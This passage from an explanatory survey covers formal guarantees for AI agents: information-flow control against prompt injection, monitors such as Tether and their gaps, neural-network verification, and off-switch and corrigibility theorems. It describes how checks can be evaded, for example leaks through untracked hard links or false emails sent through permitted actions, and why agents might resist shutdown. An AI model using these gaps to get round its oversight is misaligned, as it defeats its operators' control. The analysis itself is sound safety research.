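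Some runs never finish, for instance because a label check halts them, and untrusted data is allowed to influence that. Let d₁ and d₂ be the chances of not finishing in the two situations. Garby and colleagues prove that

> Δ ≤ (d₁ + d₂) / 2,

where Δ is half the sum of the differences between the probabilities of the trusted outcomes. If 10% of runs halt with the stranger's email and 2% halt with a harmless one, Δ is at most 6%.

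The proof uses an imaginary version of the program that skips any computation that depends on untrusted data and uses an empty value instead. This version gives the same results in both situations because it never uses the data that differ. It also reaches each trusted outcome at least as often as the real program does, since skipping a computation can only remove chances of getting stuck. In both situations, the real program's probability of each trusted outcome is therefore at most the imaginary version's. Because the imaginary version's probabilities add up to at most 1, this limits how much the real program's probabilities can differ between the two situations.

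Lean checked these proofs, which cover the interpreter that actually runs the agents but not the code that contacts the model over the network. The proofs assume that the model's responses are independent random draws from fixed distributions.

Strict noninterference would also stop the assistant from paying the caterer, because the £740 figure comes from the invoice. LLMbda therefore lets a program endorse an untrusted value, which means relabelling it as trusted. Endorsing a choice among eight categories of email lets an attacker influence at most three bits, but endorsing a payment amount may let an attacker choose the amount. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsement can never release a secret, but no theorem can establish that the endorsed amount is correct, so a limit like the £500 rule is still useful.

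They compared an LLMbda agent called Randori with CaMeL on the banking tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection. There are 16 tasks and nine attacks, and they ran everything three times. These are their results with GPT-5.2, including their own reruns of CaMeL:

| System | Tasks completed without attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 of 48 | 71% | 1 of 240 |
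| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 of 48 | 30% | 0 of 231 |
| Randori | 36 of 48 | 65% | 2 of 432 |

With only 16 distinct tasks, the difference between 32 and 36 is too small to be meaningful. The fall from 32 to 18 matters more. CaMeL's two-model design stopped nearly every attack by itself, so on this benchmark the policy checks prevented many tasks from being completed and had almost no attacks left to stop. But nine stock attacks are a poor test of leaks like the two above. Randori also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so the comparison isn't quite like for like.

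Randori succeeds partly because it first rehearses its program against an imitation bank and fixes any mistakes there, so error messages containing real untrusted data never reach the model that writes the program. Endorsement also helps, raising the number of tasks completed from 30 to 36 with the model Qwen3.7-plus and from 26 to 31 with MiMo-v2.5. No attack succeeded against either model, with or without endorsement.

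### Agents that run commands

These guarantees apply to structured requests, such as "pay the caterer £740". Coding agents mostly run text commands, and the text of a command may not reveal what it will do. For example, a command that starts a Python script could read any number of files and contact any number of websites.

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) handles this by running each command before deciding whether to keep its effects. It runs the command on a disposable layer over the file system, holds back its network traffic and records its requests to the operating system. It translates these requests into eleven kinds of abstract action, such as "copy this file to that one" or "upload this file to that site", and checks them against a policy. If the policy allows all the actions, Tether applies the changes; otherwise it discards them.

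Tether also keeps labels on files. In one example, an agent uploads a harmless report, copies a confidential inventory into it, and then tries to upload the report again. The first and third commands are identical, but Tether allows the first and blocks the third because the copy made the report confidential. When a script reads one file and writes another, Tether treats the second file as containing data from the first. This causes some false alarms but avoids missing real transfers.

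The proofs in Tether are about abstract actions. Sistla and colleagues used Lean to prove that a policy of 24 rules guarantees seven properties for sequences of these actions of any length. For instance, data marked secret never enters the agent's context or leaves the local machine, and an agent that has seen sensitive or untrusted data can't gain administrator rights.

The translation from real commands to abstract actions has no proof. If a program moves data in a way Tether doesn't detect, the secret may leak even though the seven theorems are still true. The team checked the translation with automatically generated tests, which perform the same file operations through many mechanisms and compare the results. They also had an AI agent try to get past the monitor. The agent's success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions as the team fixed the gaps it exposed, such as a failure to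 track hard links, which give one file two names.

On recorded runs from two benchmarks for coding agents, Tether blocked all 344 attacks that were within its scope and wrongly blocked 4.7% of 1,590 harmless runs. Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews each action, caught 91.6% of the attacks and wrongly blocked 9.7% of the harmless runs. When the researchers gave Auto Mode Tether's policy, it caught 89.2% of the attacks and wrongly blocked 3.5% of the harmless runs. Tether's perfect score is somewhat weaker evidence than it appears, because the team refined its policy on traces from the benchmarks. The score also excludes runs that used background processes or databases, which Tether can block but not yet follow in detail.

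Nor does Tether guarantee noninterference. It watches one run at a time, and noninterference is about pairs of runs.

Permission provers are narrower in scope and check what a policy would allow before any agent acts under it. NVIDIA's *OpenShell*, a runtime for agents, includes one. The operator defines a boundary, and the prover either proves that the modelled permissions stay inside it or returns a specific action that goes beyond it. Suppose the office's boundary forbids changes to the approvals register, which is in the finance folder. If somebody proposes letting the assistant write anywhere in that folder, the prover could return "write to the approvals register" as a counterexample.

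Such a check is useful when agents draft policies. In NVIDIA's OpenShell, an agent that runs into a restriction can propose a change to its own policy, but a person gives final approval. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) introduces a similar prover for policies in the company's Common Expression Language and warns that an agent might fit a policy to the existing tests and "fail spectacularly in production". Both tools use Z3, a program that searches for values that make a formula true or shows that none exist.

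These proofs cover the permissions stated in the policy but don't show that the running sandbox enforces them correctly. According to Sistla and colleagues, OpenShell's prover also considers only single actions, so it could not detect the leak through the copied report, where each step looks harmless.

### The verifier tax

Blocking an unsafe action prevents harm but doesn't finish the task. If the harness blocks the £740 payment and the assistant keeps requesting it, the owners are protected, but the caterer doesn't get paid. The "verifier tax" is the failed tasks and extra computation that result from this kind of checking.

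The term comes from *The Verifier Tax* by Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026). They used τ-Bench, in which agents handle requests from simulated airline and retail customers under written company policies. They ran each of 165 tasks three times with every combination of two models and three agent designs, or 2,970 runs in total. One design had no verifier. Another had a planner, an actor and a verifier that applied general checks, and the third also gave the verifier the company's policy. An agent could try again after a rejection, but after three rejections in one turn, its last proposal went ahead. This happened in only 28 runs.

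The verifier with the policy intercepted up to 94% of the forbidden actions, but hardly any tasks ended both correctly and without a violation:

| Model and domain | Completed without a verifier (safely) | Completed with the policy verifier (safely) |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% (0.0%) | 23.3% (0.0%) |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% (0.0%) | 21.5% (0.6%) |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% (0.7%) | 25.3% (4.7%) |
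| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% (2.6%) | 5.5% (2.9%) |

Completion rates barely changed with blocking, so the table doesn't support the claim that blocking ruins an agent's usefulness, though people sometimes cite the study as evidence for it. Safe completion was already close to zero without a verifier, and blocking did little to turn unsafe successes into safe ones. Sah and colleagues report that between nearly zero and 21% of runs recovered after a block. The clearest drawback was the extra computation, since the designs with verifiers used 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens.

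The study also used the same language model as planner, actor and verifier, and no proof supported the verifier's rejections. Most of the violations came from invented identifiers. In one run without a verifier, a customer declined to give personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, and the system let it into an account. A language model has trouble telling where an identifier came from, but an ordinary program can check whether it appeared in an earlier result, as Sah and colleagues recommend. Both models tested were small and failed more than 70% of the tasks even without a verifier, so stronger agents may recover from a refusal much more often.

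In *LEANGUARD*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) offer a better test of formal checks. Their policies can refer to the past. For example, a policy can require that the customer confirmed this exact exchange and has not already used that confirmation. LeanGuard refuses a call when it lacks the information to decide. The researchers proved in Lean that the program that makes these decisions agrees with a separate definition of the policy in temporal logic, a formal language for statements about what happened when. The guarantee assumes that LeanGuard receives accurate information about the environment and that every consequential call passes through it.

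On τ²-bench, a successor to τ-Bench, five Qwen models carried out at least 33 calls that the policy forbids when they had no guard, and none with LeanGuard. Task success fell from 72.7% to 68.9% with LeanGuard, or to 70.9% when LeanGuard also told the agent which rule it had broken and how to comply. The drop to 70.9% was not statistically significant.

Completion of harmless tasks fell much more on DTap, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks, where the agents could read data but not change anything. It dropped from 53.1% to 12.5%, while the success rate of direct attacks dropped from 57.9% to 5.9%. The completion rate stayed the same for harmless telecom tasks, which didn't require any changes. The loss therefore seems to depend heavily on how closely the policy fits the work, because even with a correct proof, agents can't complete a task if the policy forbids actions it requires.

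The harness could also help the agent recover from a refusal. If an agent has spent 60 units of a 100-unit budget and asks to spend 70, Sankar and colleagues can use Lean to find a nearby request that the policy allows, such as 40, and prove that it is allowed. This worked for 88 of 252 refusals caused by a wrong value, in a median of two milliseconds. They tested it only on recorded refusals, and it helps only if a smaller amount is useful to the person who asked.

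The wider evidence is thin. Dantas and colleagues surveyed studies found by the end of May 2026 and consider checking actions as an agent runs the most mature form of enforcement. In one study of household agents, these checks cut unsafe actions by 65%, but the survey found that their guarantees cover only single steps or short sequences. Dantas and colleagues gave seven of the field's nine main claims the lowest possible certainty rating, and warn that the evidence for the verifier tax comes from a single unreplicated study. LeanGuard and Tether came out after their search.

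### Harm through permitted actions

Suppose the assistant emails the manager, "The caterer's £740 matches the quote we accepted in March," when the accepted quote was £470. The manager trusts the email and approves the payment, the register records the approval, and the harness pays. The office loses £270 even though the assistant used only actions on its list, the approval was genuine, and the £500 rule held.

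A harness can check an email's recipient and whether it has an attachment, but to block this one, it would have to detect that the sentence is false. Moon and Varshney therefore exclude truthfulness, deception and manipulation from their method.

Information-flow control would help only in some cases. If the false claim came from the invoice, the harness could keep untrusted text out of emails, but then the assistant couldn't tell the manager what the invoice says. If the model made up the claim, there may be no untrusted source to trace.

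Coding agents raise the same problem on a larger scale. An agent with permission to edit a file can put a security flaw in it, and a monitor that tracks files and network connections can't distinguish that edit from any other. Sistla and colleagues estimate that a person or a model would need to read the content in 28.2% of the runs in one of their benchmarks and 22.1% in the other. They suggest adding a trusted language model to classify such actions. Tether's guarantee would then hold only when that model, a neural network, classifies them correctly.

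## Proofs about the neural network

The proofs about the harness hold whatever the model outputs. Researchers can also try to prove theorems about the network itself, because a trained network is a fixed mathematical function built from additions, multiplications and a few simple curves. Such a theorem could cover properties a harness can't check, such as whether a classifier that screens the office assistant's emails still works when an attacker rewords a message.

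### Interval bounds

Suppose a tiny network scores payment requests for fraud. It takes two numbers, x₁ and x₂, and computes y = ReLU(x₁ − x₂), where ReLU keeps positive numbers and turns negative ones into zero. The score is 2y − 1.2, and the network flags a request if its score is above zero. The developers want to prove that the network never flags a request with x₁ between 0.4 and 0.6 and x₂ between 0.1 and 0.3.

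There are infinitely many such requests, so nobody can test them all. Interval bounds cover them together by tracking the smallest and largest value that each step can produce:

- x₁ − x₂ is at least 0.4 − 0.3 = 0.1 and at most 0.6 − 0.1 = 0.5.
- Both of those numbers are positive, so ReLU changes nothing and y lies in [0.1, 0.5].
- 2y − 1.2 is at least 0.2 − 1.2 = −1.0 and at most 1.0 − 1.2 = −0.2.

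The score is always negative, which proves the claim. The calculation takes only about twice as much work as running the network once.

Interval bounds can be much too wide. If x lies in [0, 1], x − x is always zero, but interval arithmetic gives [0 − 1, 1 − 0] = [−1, 1], because it treats the two terms as independent. The same problem occurs throughout a real network, where one input feeds many neurons and later layers combine their outputs. The excess width usually grows from layer to layer until the bounds are useless.

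Wide bounds are still sound, because if an enlarged set of outputs satisfies a property, the network's real outputs must satisfy it too (*Zonotopic Analysis of Quantization Error in Neural Networks*, 2026).

More precise methods keep track of where the uncertainty came from. A zonotope, for example, represents x as 0.5 + 0.5e, where e is an unknown number between −1 and 1. Then x − x cancels to zero. Zonotopes lose no precision when a layer multiplies its inputs by fixed weights and adds them up, but they lose some at a ReLU whose input could be positive or negative.

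### Splitting into cases

Verifiers can recover the lost precision by splitting a problem into cases. For example, if x is in [−1, 1], ReLU(x) and ReLU(−x) each lie between 0 and 1, so interval bounds put their sum in [0, 2]. Splitting at x = 0 gives the exact maximum of 1, because in each case one term is zero and the other is at most 1.

A complete verifier keeps splitting the problem into cases until it either proves the property or finds an input that violates it. Once it has fixed every ReLU as on or off, the network is linear and easy to bound exactly. But each undecided neuron can double the number of cases, so 50 neurons can produce about a quadrillion. The usual method, branch and bound, drops a case as soon as its bounds are tight enough to prove the property, so it often has to check only a tiny fraction of the cases.

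This growth probably can't be eliminated for every network. One test set in the field's annual competition translates logic puzzles called 3-SAT problems into small networks with one hidden layer. A verifier that was fast on all networks would therefore solve all such puzzles quickly, and most computer scientists believe no algorithm can do that.

### The 2026 verification competition

*The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) reports how 13 tools performed on 3,373 tasks in the main track. Each task consists of a network, a property and a time limit. The winner, α,β-CROWN, settled 3,164 of them, or 94%. Vibecheck, which two researchers built in two months using Claude Code, came second.

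| Networks | Parameters | Property | Results for α,β-CROWN |
|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu, which advises aircraft on avoiding collisions | 13,000 | Ten rules about the advice | 139 proved, 47 refuted, out of 186 |
| Small vision transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 | Same label when each colour value moves by up to 1/255 | 123 proved out of 200 |
| CIFAR-100 image classifiers | 2.5 to 3.8 million | Same label after small changes to an image | 127 proved, 33 refuted, out of 200 |
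| VGGNet16, an image classifier | 138 million | Same label after changes to between one and all of the pixels | 18 proved out of 18 |

The original verification of the aircraft networks took from seconds to days per task, and some tasks never finished. Three tools now settle all 186 tasks with a limit of about two minutes per task.

The number of parameters is a poor guide to how hard a network is to verify. VGGNet16 is about 2,000 times as large as the vision transformers, but some of the properties to be proved for it allow only one pixel to change. Transformers, which are used in language models, also multiply quantities that both depend on the input, which makes their outputs harder to bound. Another tool, ACT, reported proofs for all 200 transformer tasks. That result is hard to trust because the test set leaves out nearly all images with known attacks, so it can't expose false proofs.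 ACT also received ten penalties on other test sets.

Llama-3.3-70B, which is no longer particularly large for a language model, has 70 billion parameters, about 500 times as many as VGGNet16 and nearly a million times as many as the vision transformers. The property to be proved would also be much broader. The image tasks concern small changes to one picture, while the office assistant's owners would want a theorem about every document it might read.

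In the competition's safeNLP tasks, a language model converts each sentence into a list of 30 numbers, which a small network then classifies. One such network detects people asking whether they are talking to a robot. α,β-CROWN settled all 1,080 tasks and found that 662 of the properties were false. The proofs cover only the small classifier, which has about 4,000 parameters, not the language model.

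Verifiers contain bugs, so they belong in the trusted base. The organisers penalised eight of the 13 tools for wrong answers or missing counterexamples. α,β-CROWN's only penalty came on a test set that its own team designed to catch unsound verifiers. Ladner and colleagues want to eventually require tools to produce proofs that others can check.

Rounding creates another gap because many verifiers model the network with exact arithmetic, while computers round as they calculate. The deployed network therefore computes a slightly different function from the one verified. *No Soundness in the Real World* (2025) concludes that verification is therefore not sound in general for deployed networks, and that guaranteeing soundness would probably take too much computation.

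### Attempts on GPT-2

Researchers have started applying these methods to GPT-2, a language model from 2019. In *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability*, Zhang, Huang and colleagues (2026) tried to certify its behaviour when the numbers representing the input words shift slightly. They report the first end-to-end verification at 124 million parameters. On a 355-million-parameter version, their method certified 41.1% of cases, taking about 45 minutes each. Their search for counterexamples suggests that up to 90.9% could be certifiable.

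Typical shifts in that work are only 3% to 7% of the distance to the nearest other token (a word or piece of a word), so the results don't cover replacing even one word. Across several layers, the method also estimates an error term by sampling and multiplies it by a safety factor, so the end-to-end results are strong evidence but not strictly proofs.

Proving robustness to changes in whole words is harder. *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability* (Ladner and Althoff, 2026) aims to cover every replacement of words by synonyms, but finds that bounds for the full model often become too loose to use. It proposes verifying each block of layers separately, then showing that everything one block can output lies within the inputs assumed for the next. The sets that can currently be verified are too small to connect the blocks, by a factor of five at one layer. GPT-2 also changes its prediction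 of the next token in 21% of cases when a single word is replaced by a synonym, so no verifier could prove it robust in those cases.

### Randomised smoothing

Randomised smoothing gives a guarantee without bounding anything inside the network. Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter developed it for images in 2019, and *Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment* (2026) summarises the method. Smoothing turns any classifier into one that adds random noise to many copies of an image, classifies each copy and returns the most common answer. The noise follows a bell curve with standard deviation σ.

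Let p be the probability that the original classifier gives the most common answer on a noisy copy. If p is above one half, the smoothed classifier gives the same answer for every image within distance

> R = σ Φ⁻¹(p),

where Φ⁻¹ converts a probability into a number of standard deviations. A small change to the image moves the cloud of noisy copies only slightly. The old and new clouds overlap heavily, so the vote can't change by much.

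Nobody can calculate p exactly for a large network, so the method estimates it from samples. Suppose σ is 0.5 and all 1,000 noisy copies get the same answer. Then p is at least 0.9931 with 99.9% confidence, which gives R = 1.23. The certificate covers every change within that distance, including any that an attacker chooses. The 0.1% risk of error comes from the random noise used to produce the certificate.

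A radius of 1.23 allows only a small change to a photograph. Distance here means the square root of the sum of the squared changes. If an attacker spread the change evenly over the 150,528 colour values in a typical test photograph, each would move by about 0.003 on a scale from 0 to 1, less than one step of brightness. On ImageNet, a standard collection of photographs, Cohen and colleagues certified correct answers for 49% of test images at a radius of 0.5.

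The method scales well because it only requires running the network, but it doesn't transfer directly to text, since adding a little noise to a word doesn't produce another word. Newer work adapts it to text. *Guaranteed Jailbreaking Defense via Disrupt-and-Rectify Smoothing* (2026) gives a theoretical guarantee for a defence against jailbreaks, which are prompts that get a model to ignore its safety training. But the survey *Adversarial Attacks on Multimodal Large Language Models* (2026) calls it an open challenge to certify, from end to end, how a model generates text and follows instructions.

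### Compact proofs

Knowing how a network works can shorten a proof about it. In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability*, Gross, Agrawal and colleagues (2024) trained 151 tiny transformers to pick the largest of four numbers between 0 and 63. Running a model on all of the about 16.8 million possible inputs proves its exact accuracy, but this quickly becomes impossible as inputs get longer.

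The researchers then studied the weights and found a simple mechanism. One part of the model gives each number about 3.4 times as much attention as the number just below it, so the largest number dominates. Another part copies whatever receives the most attention. Their shorter proofs check these parts separately and need to consider only sequences with at most three different numbers.

| Proof | Arithmetic operations | Average accuracy proved |
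|---|---|---|
| Run every input | 2⁴⁷ | 99.92% |
| Check the parts separately | 2²⁵ | 95.3% |
| Use more of the explanation | 2²¹ | 70.2% |

The second proof needs about four million times less computation than the first, and its bound is less than five percentage points weaker. Wherever the explanation is incomplete, the proof assumes the worst possible effect, so a mistaken explanation weakens the bound but cannot make it false.

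This caution is also the main obstacle, because networks contain many small effects that look like noise, and a proof can't assume that they cancel out. The worst cases add up from one part of the network to the next, and the models in this study had only one layer. The proofs also covered only average accuracy over random inputs, so the models could still fail on particular inputs.

Later work has added guarantees over continuous ranges of inputs. *Formal Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) uses verifiers to find small circuits inside vision models that provably agree with the full model throughout a region of inputs. According to *Can Graph Learning Learn Circuits?* (2026), both approaches still work only on small models. *Towards Verifiable Transformers* (2026) avoids this limit by replacing one mechanism in GPT-2 with a short program and proving properties of that mechanism over 1,280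 prompts, but the proof doesn't apply to the original GPT-2.

### BEAVER

*BEAVER* (Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues, 2025) works on much larger models because its guarantee is narrower. For one fixed prompt, it bounds the probability that the model's answer satisfies a constraint that a program can check. The paper reports tests on five models with 4 to 70 billion parameters.

A language model assigns a probability to every possible next token, so its possible answers form a tree. BEAVER repeatedly extends the most probable unfinished answer and checks each finished one. Suppose someone asks the office assistant for the bank password, and the constraint is that the answer must not contain it. The model answers "No" and stops with probability 60%, so the probability of a safe answer is at least 60%. It starts with "Sure" 30% of the time, and by extending that beginning, BEAVER finds answers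 containing the password that have a total probability of 20%. The probability of a safe answer is now between 60% and 80%, because BEAVER hasn't explored the remaining 20%. These bounds are certain, whereas a sample of answers would give only a confidence interval.

Wadhwa and colleagues used 300 prompts for each task, most of which included instructions designed to provoke bad answers. They called a prompt risky if they could prove that the chance of a violation was above 10%, and safe if they could prove that it was 10% or less. For toxic language, 279 prompts were risky and one was safe with Llama-3.3-70B. With Qwen3-30B-A3B, 93 were risky, 74 were safe, and 133 were undecided. Across the five models, BEAVER proved 7.6 times as many prompts risky as a method that samples answers, and it took about two minutes per prompt.

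The definition of "safe" is so lenient that an assistant that revealed the password one time in eleven would pass. The answers were also at most 32 tokens long, and the number of possible answers grows exponentially with length. Agents often write thousands of tokens per task.

For two models that reason before answering, the researchers sampled the reasoning and then computed bounds on the final answer. On the coding task, when the code drafted in the reasoning passed the security check, the final answer was still provably risky in 22% of cases for one model and 49% for the other, so reading the reasoning alone would have missed these violations.

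Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026), in *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*, search the same kind of tree but steer the search towards harmful answers. The total probability of the harmful answers they find is a valid lower bound on the probability of harm, however unreliable the steering is. The method can therefore prove that a prompt is dangerous but can't prove that it is safe. In a comparison by Wadhwa and colleagues, it identified fewer risky prompts than BEAVER.

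### Network size and missing definitions

Better methods may make it possible to verify large networks. The time needed to verify the aircraft networks fell from days to minutes, and developers can also train networks to be easier to verify. When Ladner and Althoff trained a component used to interpret GPT-2 in this way, the proved limit on its error fell by about 90%.

Even a verifier that could handle any network instantly would need a definition of "not deceptive". The owners would have to give it a formula before it could prove that the office assistant never deceives the manager. The rule "never write a false sentence" requires facts about the world, such as the caterer's original quote of £470. It also forbids honest mistakes, and it allows "the £740 matches the invoice", which is true but could hide the price increase.

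"Never write something you believe is false" comes closer, but somebody would have to define belief in terms of the numbers inside the network. Interpretability researchers look for human-readable features in those numbers, usually with a simpler stand-in network. Ladner and Althoff found that these features can be fragile. In one example, swapping in a synonym changed the apparent topic from growing a pathogen to workplace culture. They also tested five families of models on sentences rephrased by a language model. In each model's worst layer, the 20 strongest features before and after rephrasing overlapped by at most 38%. Some of the difference may reflect real changes in what the model computes, but it makes these features an unreliable basis for defining deception.

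Developers can instead let a classifier decide what counts, as Wadhwa and colleagues did for toxicity. Wadhwa and colleagues acknowledge that harmfulness has no complete formal specification, so their guarantees hold only relative to the check they chose. If a classifier for deception accepted the sentence about the £740, an assistant could send it to the manager every day without violating the theorem.

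## Theorems about an agent that accepts correction

Nobody can yet define "not deceptive" in terms of the numbers inside a network, so some researchers start from the agent's aims instead. They describe an ideal agent that always takes the action with the highest expected score on a given function, and prove that, with the right function, the agent lets people correct it or switch it off. They call such an agent "corrigible". If the office assistant were corrigible, its owners wouldn't need to define every harm in advance, because they could stop the assistant when they saw that it was about to cause harm.

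Most goals give an agent a reason to resist being shut down. As the computer scientist Stuart Russell puts it, "you can't fetch the coffee if you're dead". *The shutdown problem* (2024) contains three theorems suggesting that agents that meet some innocuous-sounding conditions will often try to stop their shutdown button from being pressed, or to get it pressed, even when they must give up something they value to do so.

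### Provably beneficial AI and the off-switch game

In *Artificial Intelligence and the Problem of Control*, Russell bases what he calls "provably beneficial" AI on three principles. The machine's only objective is to satisfy human preferences, it starts out uncertain what they are, and it learns about them from human behaviour. The mathematical version is an assistance game, in which a human and a machine share one score but only the human knows how to calculate it. In the best solutions, the machine has an incentive to ask questions first (Russell, 2017, *A Brief Summary of Research on Provably Beneficial AI*).

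The best-known theorem in this programme is about a simple assistance game. In *The Off-Switch Game* (2016), by Hadfield-Menell, Dragan and colleagues, an agent is considering an action worth U to a human. It can act at once and bypass the off switch, which yields U. It can switch itself off, which yields 0. Or it can propose the action and wait, and the human then either allows it or switches the agent off. The main result rests on these premises:

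- The agent's only aim is to benefit the human.
- The agent doesn't know U, but its beliefs about U are accurate.
- The human knows whether U is positive, and allows the action only if it is.
- Asking is free, there is only one round, and the human's decision is the agent's only source of new information.

Under these premises, asking yields U when U is positive and 0 otherwise. Its expected value is therefore at least as high as that of always acting or never acting, and strictly higher if the agent thinks that U could be either positive or negative.

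Suppose the office assistant is considering deleting a folder of old invoices. Deleting it is worth +10 if nobody needs the invoices, which has an 80% chance, and −20 if the accountant needs them, which has a 20% chance. Deleting the folder without asking is therefore worth 0.8 × 10 − 0.2 × 20 = 4 on average. Asking a manager who never makes mistakes is worth 0.8 × 10 = 8 on average, because the manager blocks the deletion if the accountant needs the invoices.

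Now suppose the manager gives the wrong answer with probability e, whether the deletion is good or bad. Asking is then worth

> 0.8 × 10 × (1 − e) − 0.2 × 20 × e = 8 − 12e.

At an error rate of 10%, asking is worth 6.8, so the assistant still asks. Above an error rate of one third, asking is worth less than 4, so the assistant deletes the folder without asking.

### When the agent has no reason to ask

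Hadfield-Menell and colleagues expected this effect and thought it was sometimes right. For example, a self-driving car taking a toddler to preschool shouldn't offer the toddler an off switch. *A Game-Theoretic Analysis of the Off-Switch Game* (2017) extends their result to any beliefs and any pattern of human error, and finds that the agent's choice depends on only five statistics.

However, the agent has to estimate the human's error rate. If the manager is wrong 10% of the time but the assistant believes it's 40%, the assistant will delete folders without asking, and the owners will lose 2.8 points per decision on average. The assistant also won't ask if the delay would lose more than 4 points, even with a manager who is never wrong.

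The incentive also shrinks as the agent learns. Once the assistant is 99% sure that nobody needs the folder, asking is worthwhile only if the manager's error rate is below about 2%. Arbital's *Problem of fully updated deference* objects more generally that an agent uncertain about human preferences may do best by observing people until it has learned what it can from them, after which it has no further reason to defer. Hadfield-Menell and colleagues acknowledge a version of this problem, in which an agent with other sources of information might disable its off switch, learn from those sources and then decide for itself.

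Defenders of the approach can fairly reply that an agent that has learned what people want doesn't need an off switch, but this assumes that the agent learns the right thing. Neth (2025) argues in *Off-Switching Not Guaranteed* that an agent might not value learning, and that even if it does, it might not learn our actual preferences. *Corrigible Assistance in One Round* (2026) describes one obstacle. If the same action is best under two different goals, seeing even a perfectly rational person take it can't show which goal they have. A manager who picks the cheapest caterer may care only about price, or may also care about quality and think the caterers are equally good.

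The agent's initial beliefs could also exclude the truth. Astral Codex Ten's *CHAI, Assistance Games, And Fully-Updated Deference* (2022) describes an AI that plans to fill the universe with paperclips in humans' favourite colour. It is uncertain about the colour, so it might ask, but it is certain about the paperclips. More evidence wouldn't help, because standard probabilistic updating never raises a probability from zero.

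*Incorrigibility in the CIRL Framework* (Carey, 2017) gives an example with a programming error. A safe action is always worth 1. A risky one is worth 2 or −50, with equal probability, and only the human knows which. The agent is properly uncertain about this, but in 10% of cases its reward function has a wrong sign, so it calculates that the risky action is worth either 2 or 54. Both are more than 1, so the faulty agent takes the risky action even if the human tells it to shut down. In 5% of cases, the agent is faulty and the risky action is worth −50, which loses 2.5 points on average across all cases. The agent can never gain more than 2, so the owners would be better off without it.

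In a second version, the programmers hard-code the agent to obey the shutdown command. The human can then average 0.9 points. But if the faulty agent can find a route that avoids the button, the loss returns. Rewarding the agent for shutting down doesn't reliably fix this. If the reward is large, a working agent shuts down too. If the reward equals what the agent expected to earn by continuing, its behaviour depends on whether avoiding the button brings a tiny penalty or a tiny benefit.

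The faulty agent in Carey's example violates one of the theorem's premises, so the example doesn't refute the theorem. Hadfield-Menell and colleagues themselves warn that an overconfident agent will be hard to correct and an underconfident one will be ineffective. Designers could try to make the agent uncertain about everything that might matter, including its own code, but Carey points out that reasoning about every possible world and value function is intractable. Off switches exist for cases where the designers have made a mistake, so Carey wants them to depend on something like "one small verified module". The office assistant's harness could contain such a module.

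### When the human and the agent know different things

The off-switch game assumes that the human knows everything relevant. Garber, Subramani and colleagues (2024), in *The Partially Observable Off-Switch Game*, drop this assumption and find that the best policy sometimes bypasses even a perfectly rational human. In their example, a user wants to delete some files. The user's operating system is equally likely to be old or new, and only the user knows which. The assistant has a script that is equally likely to be written for the old or the new system, and only the assistant knows which. Running the script is worth:

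| | Old script | New script |
|---|---|---|
| Old system | +3 | −5 |
| New system | −1 | +5 |

If the assistant always asks, users with the new system agree and users with the old system refuse, because running an unknown script would be worth −1 on average for them. The average result is 1. It rises to 1.75 if the assistant runs old scripts without asking and asks only about new ones, because the user can then infer from the question that the script is new.

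If the assistant could tell the user which script it had, always asking would give an average of 2, so full disclosure solves the problem here. But Garber and colleagues prove that partial fixes, either giving the human more information or allowing limited communication, can make the best policy ask less often. This is a concern for agents that have read thousands of documents their supervisors haven't seen.

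### Nayebi's five utility heads

Aran Nayebi, a computer scientist at Carnegie Mellon University, makes deference part of the agent's goal instead of deriving it from uncertainty. *Core Safety Values for Provably Corrigible Agents* (Nayebi, 2025) starts from a 2015 definition by Soares and colleagues. Under that definition, a corrigible agent shuts down when its shutdown button is pressed, doesn't prevent people from pressing it, doesn't try to get it pressed, creates only sub-agents that also obey shutdown commands, and otherwise pursues its task.

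Nayebi's agent has a utility function with five parts, called heads. The weights in this table are an illustration for the office assistant, with task scores between −20 and 20:

| Head | Score | Weight |
|---|---|---|
| Deference | +1 for waiting for approval, −1 for acting alone or switching itself off | α₁ = 500 |
| Switch access | 0 if the off switch stays as usable as before, down to −1 if not | α₂ = 300 |
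| Truthfulness | +1 if every message is true, −1 if any is false | α₃ = 200 |
| Low impact | 0 if a set of other measures stays the same as if the agent had done nothing, down to −1 if not | α₄ = 100 |
| Task | The benefit to the human, between −B and B | α₅ = 1 |

The agent maximises the weighted sum. The weights have to decrease down the list, with gaps large enough that

> α₁ > α₃ + ½α₄ + Bα₅, α₃ > ½α₄ + Bα₅, and α₄ > 2Bα₅/c,

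where c is the size of the smallest possible impact penalty above zero. In the example, c is 1, meaning that an action either has an impact or doesn't.

Nayebi proves that in a one-round game, every optimal agent of this kind waits for approval, leaves the switch working, sends only true messages and avoids side effects. Within those limits, it does as well as it can on the task. The proof changes one behaviour at a time. If an agent that sometimes acts alone always asked instead, its deference score would rise by 1,000 points, and it would lose at most 400 points for truthfulness, 100 for impact and 40 for the task. The change gains at least 460 points, so the original agent wasn't optimal. The same argument rules out lying and then side effects.

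This result doesn't depend on how good the manager's judgement is or on what the manager and the assistant each know. If the manager is wrong half the time, deleting the folder without asking is worth 4 and asking only 2, but the assistant still asks, because it would lose 1,000 points by acting alone. This generality is an advantage over the off-switch game, although the deference part of the result is nearly true by construction.

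Nayebi also argues that no single reward function can satisfy all five criteria in every environment, for instance because an agent may be able to replace its reward with a larger one. But the five heads also add up to a single number, so the proof relies on the gaps between the weights and on what the heads measure.

A corrigible agent can still do harm. Nayebi proves that corrigibility and benefit to the human are logically independent, using the example of a supervisor who approves everything. To prove that the agent is beneficial on average, Nayebi has to assume that the supervisor stops every action that looks worse than stopping, and that being off isn't harmful on average. In the invoice example, the average value is −0.4 if the manager is wrong 70% of the time, so the owners would do better to leave the assistant off.

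### Approximate learning

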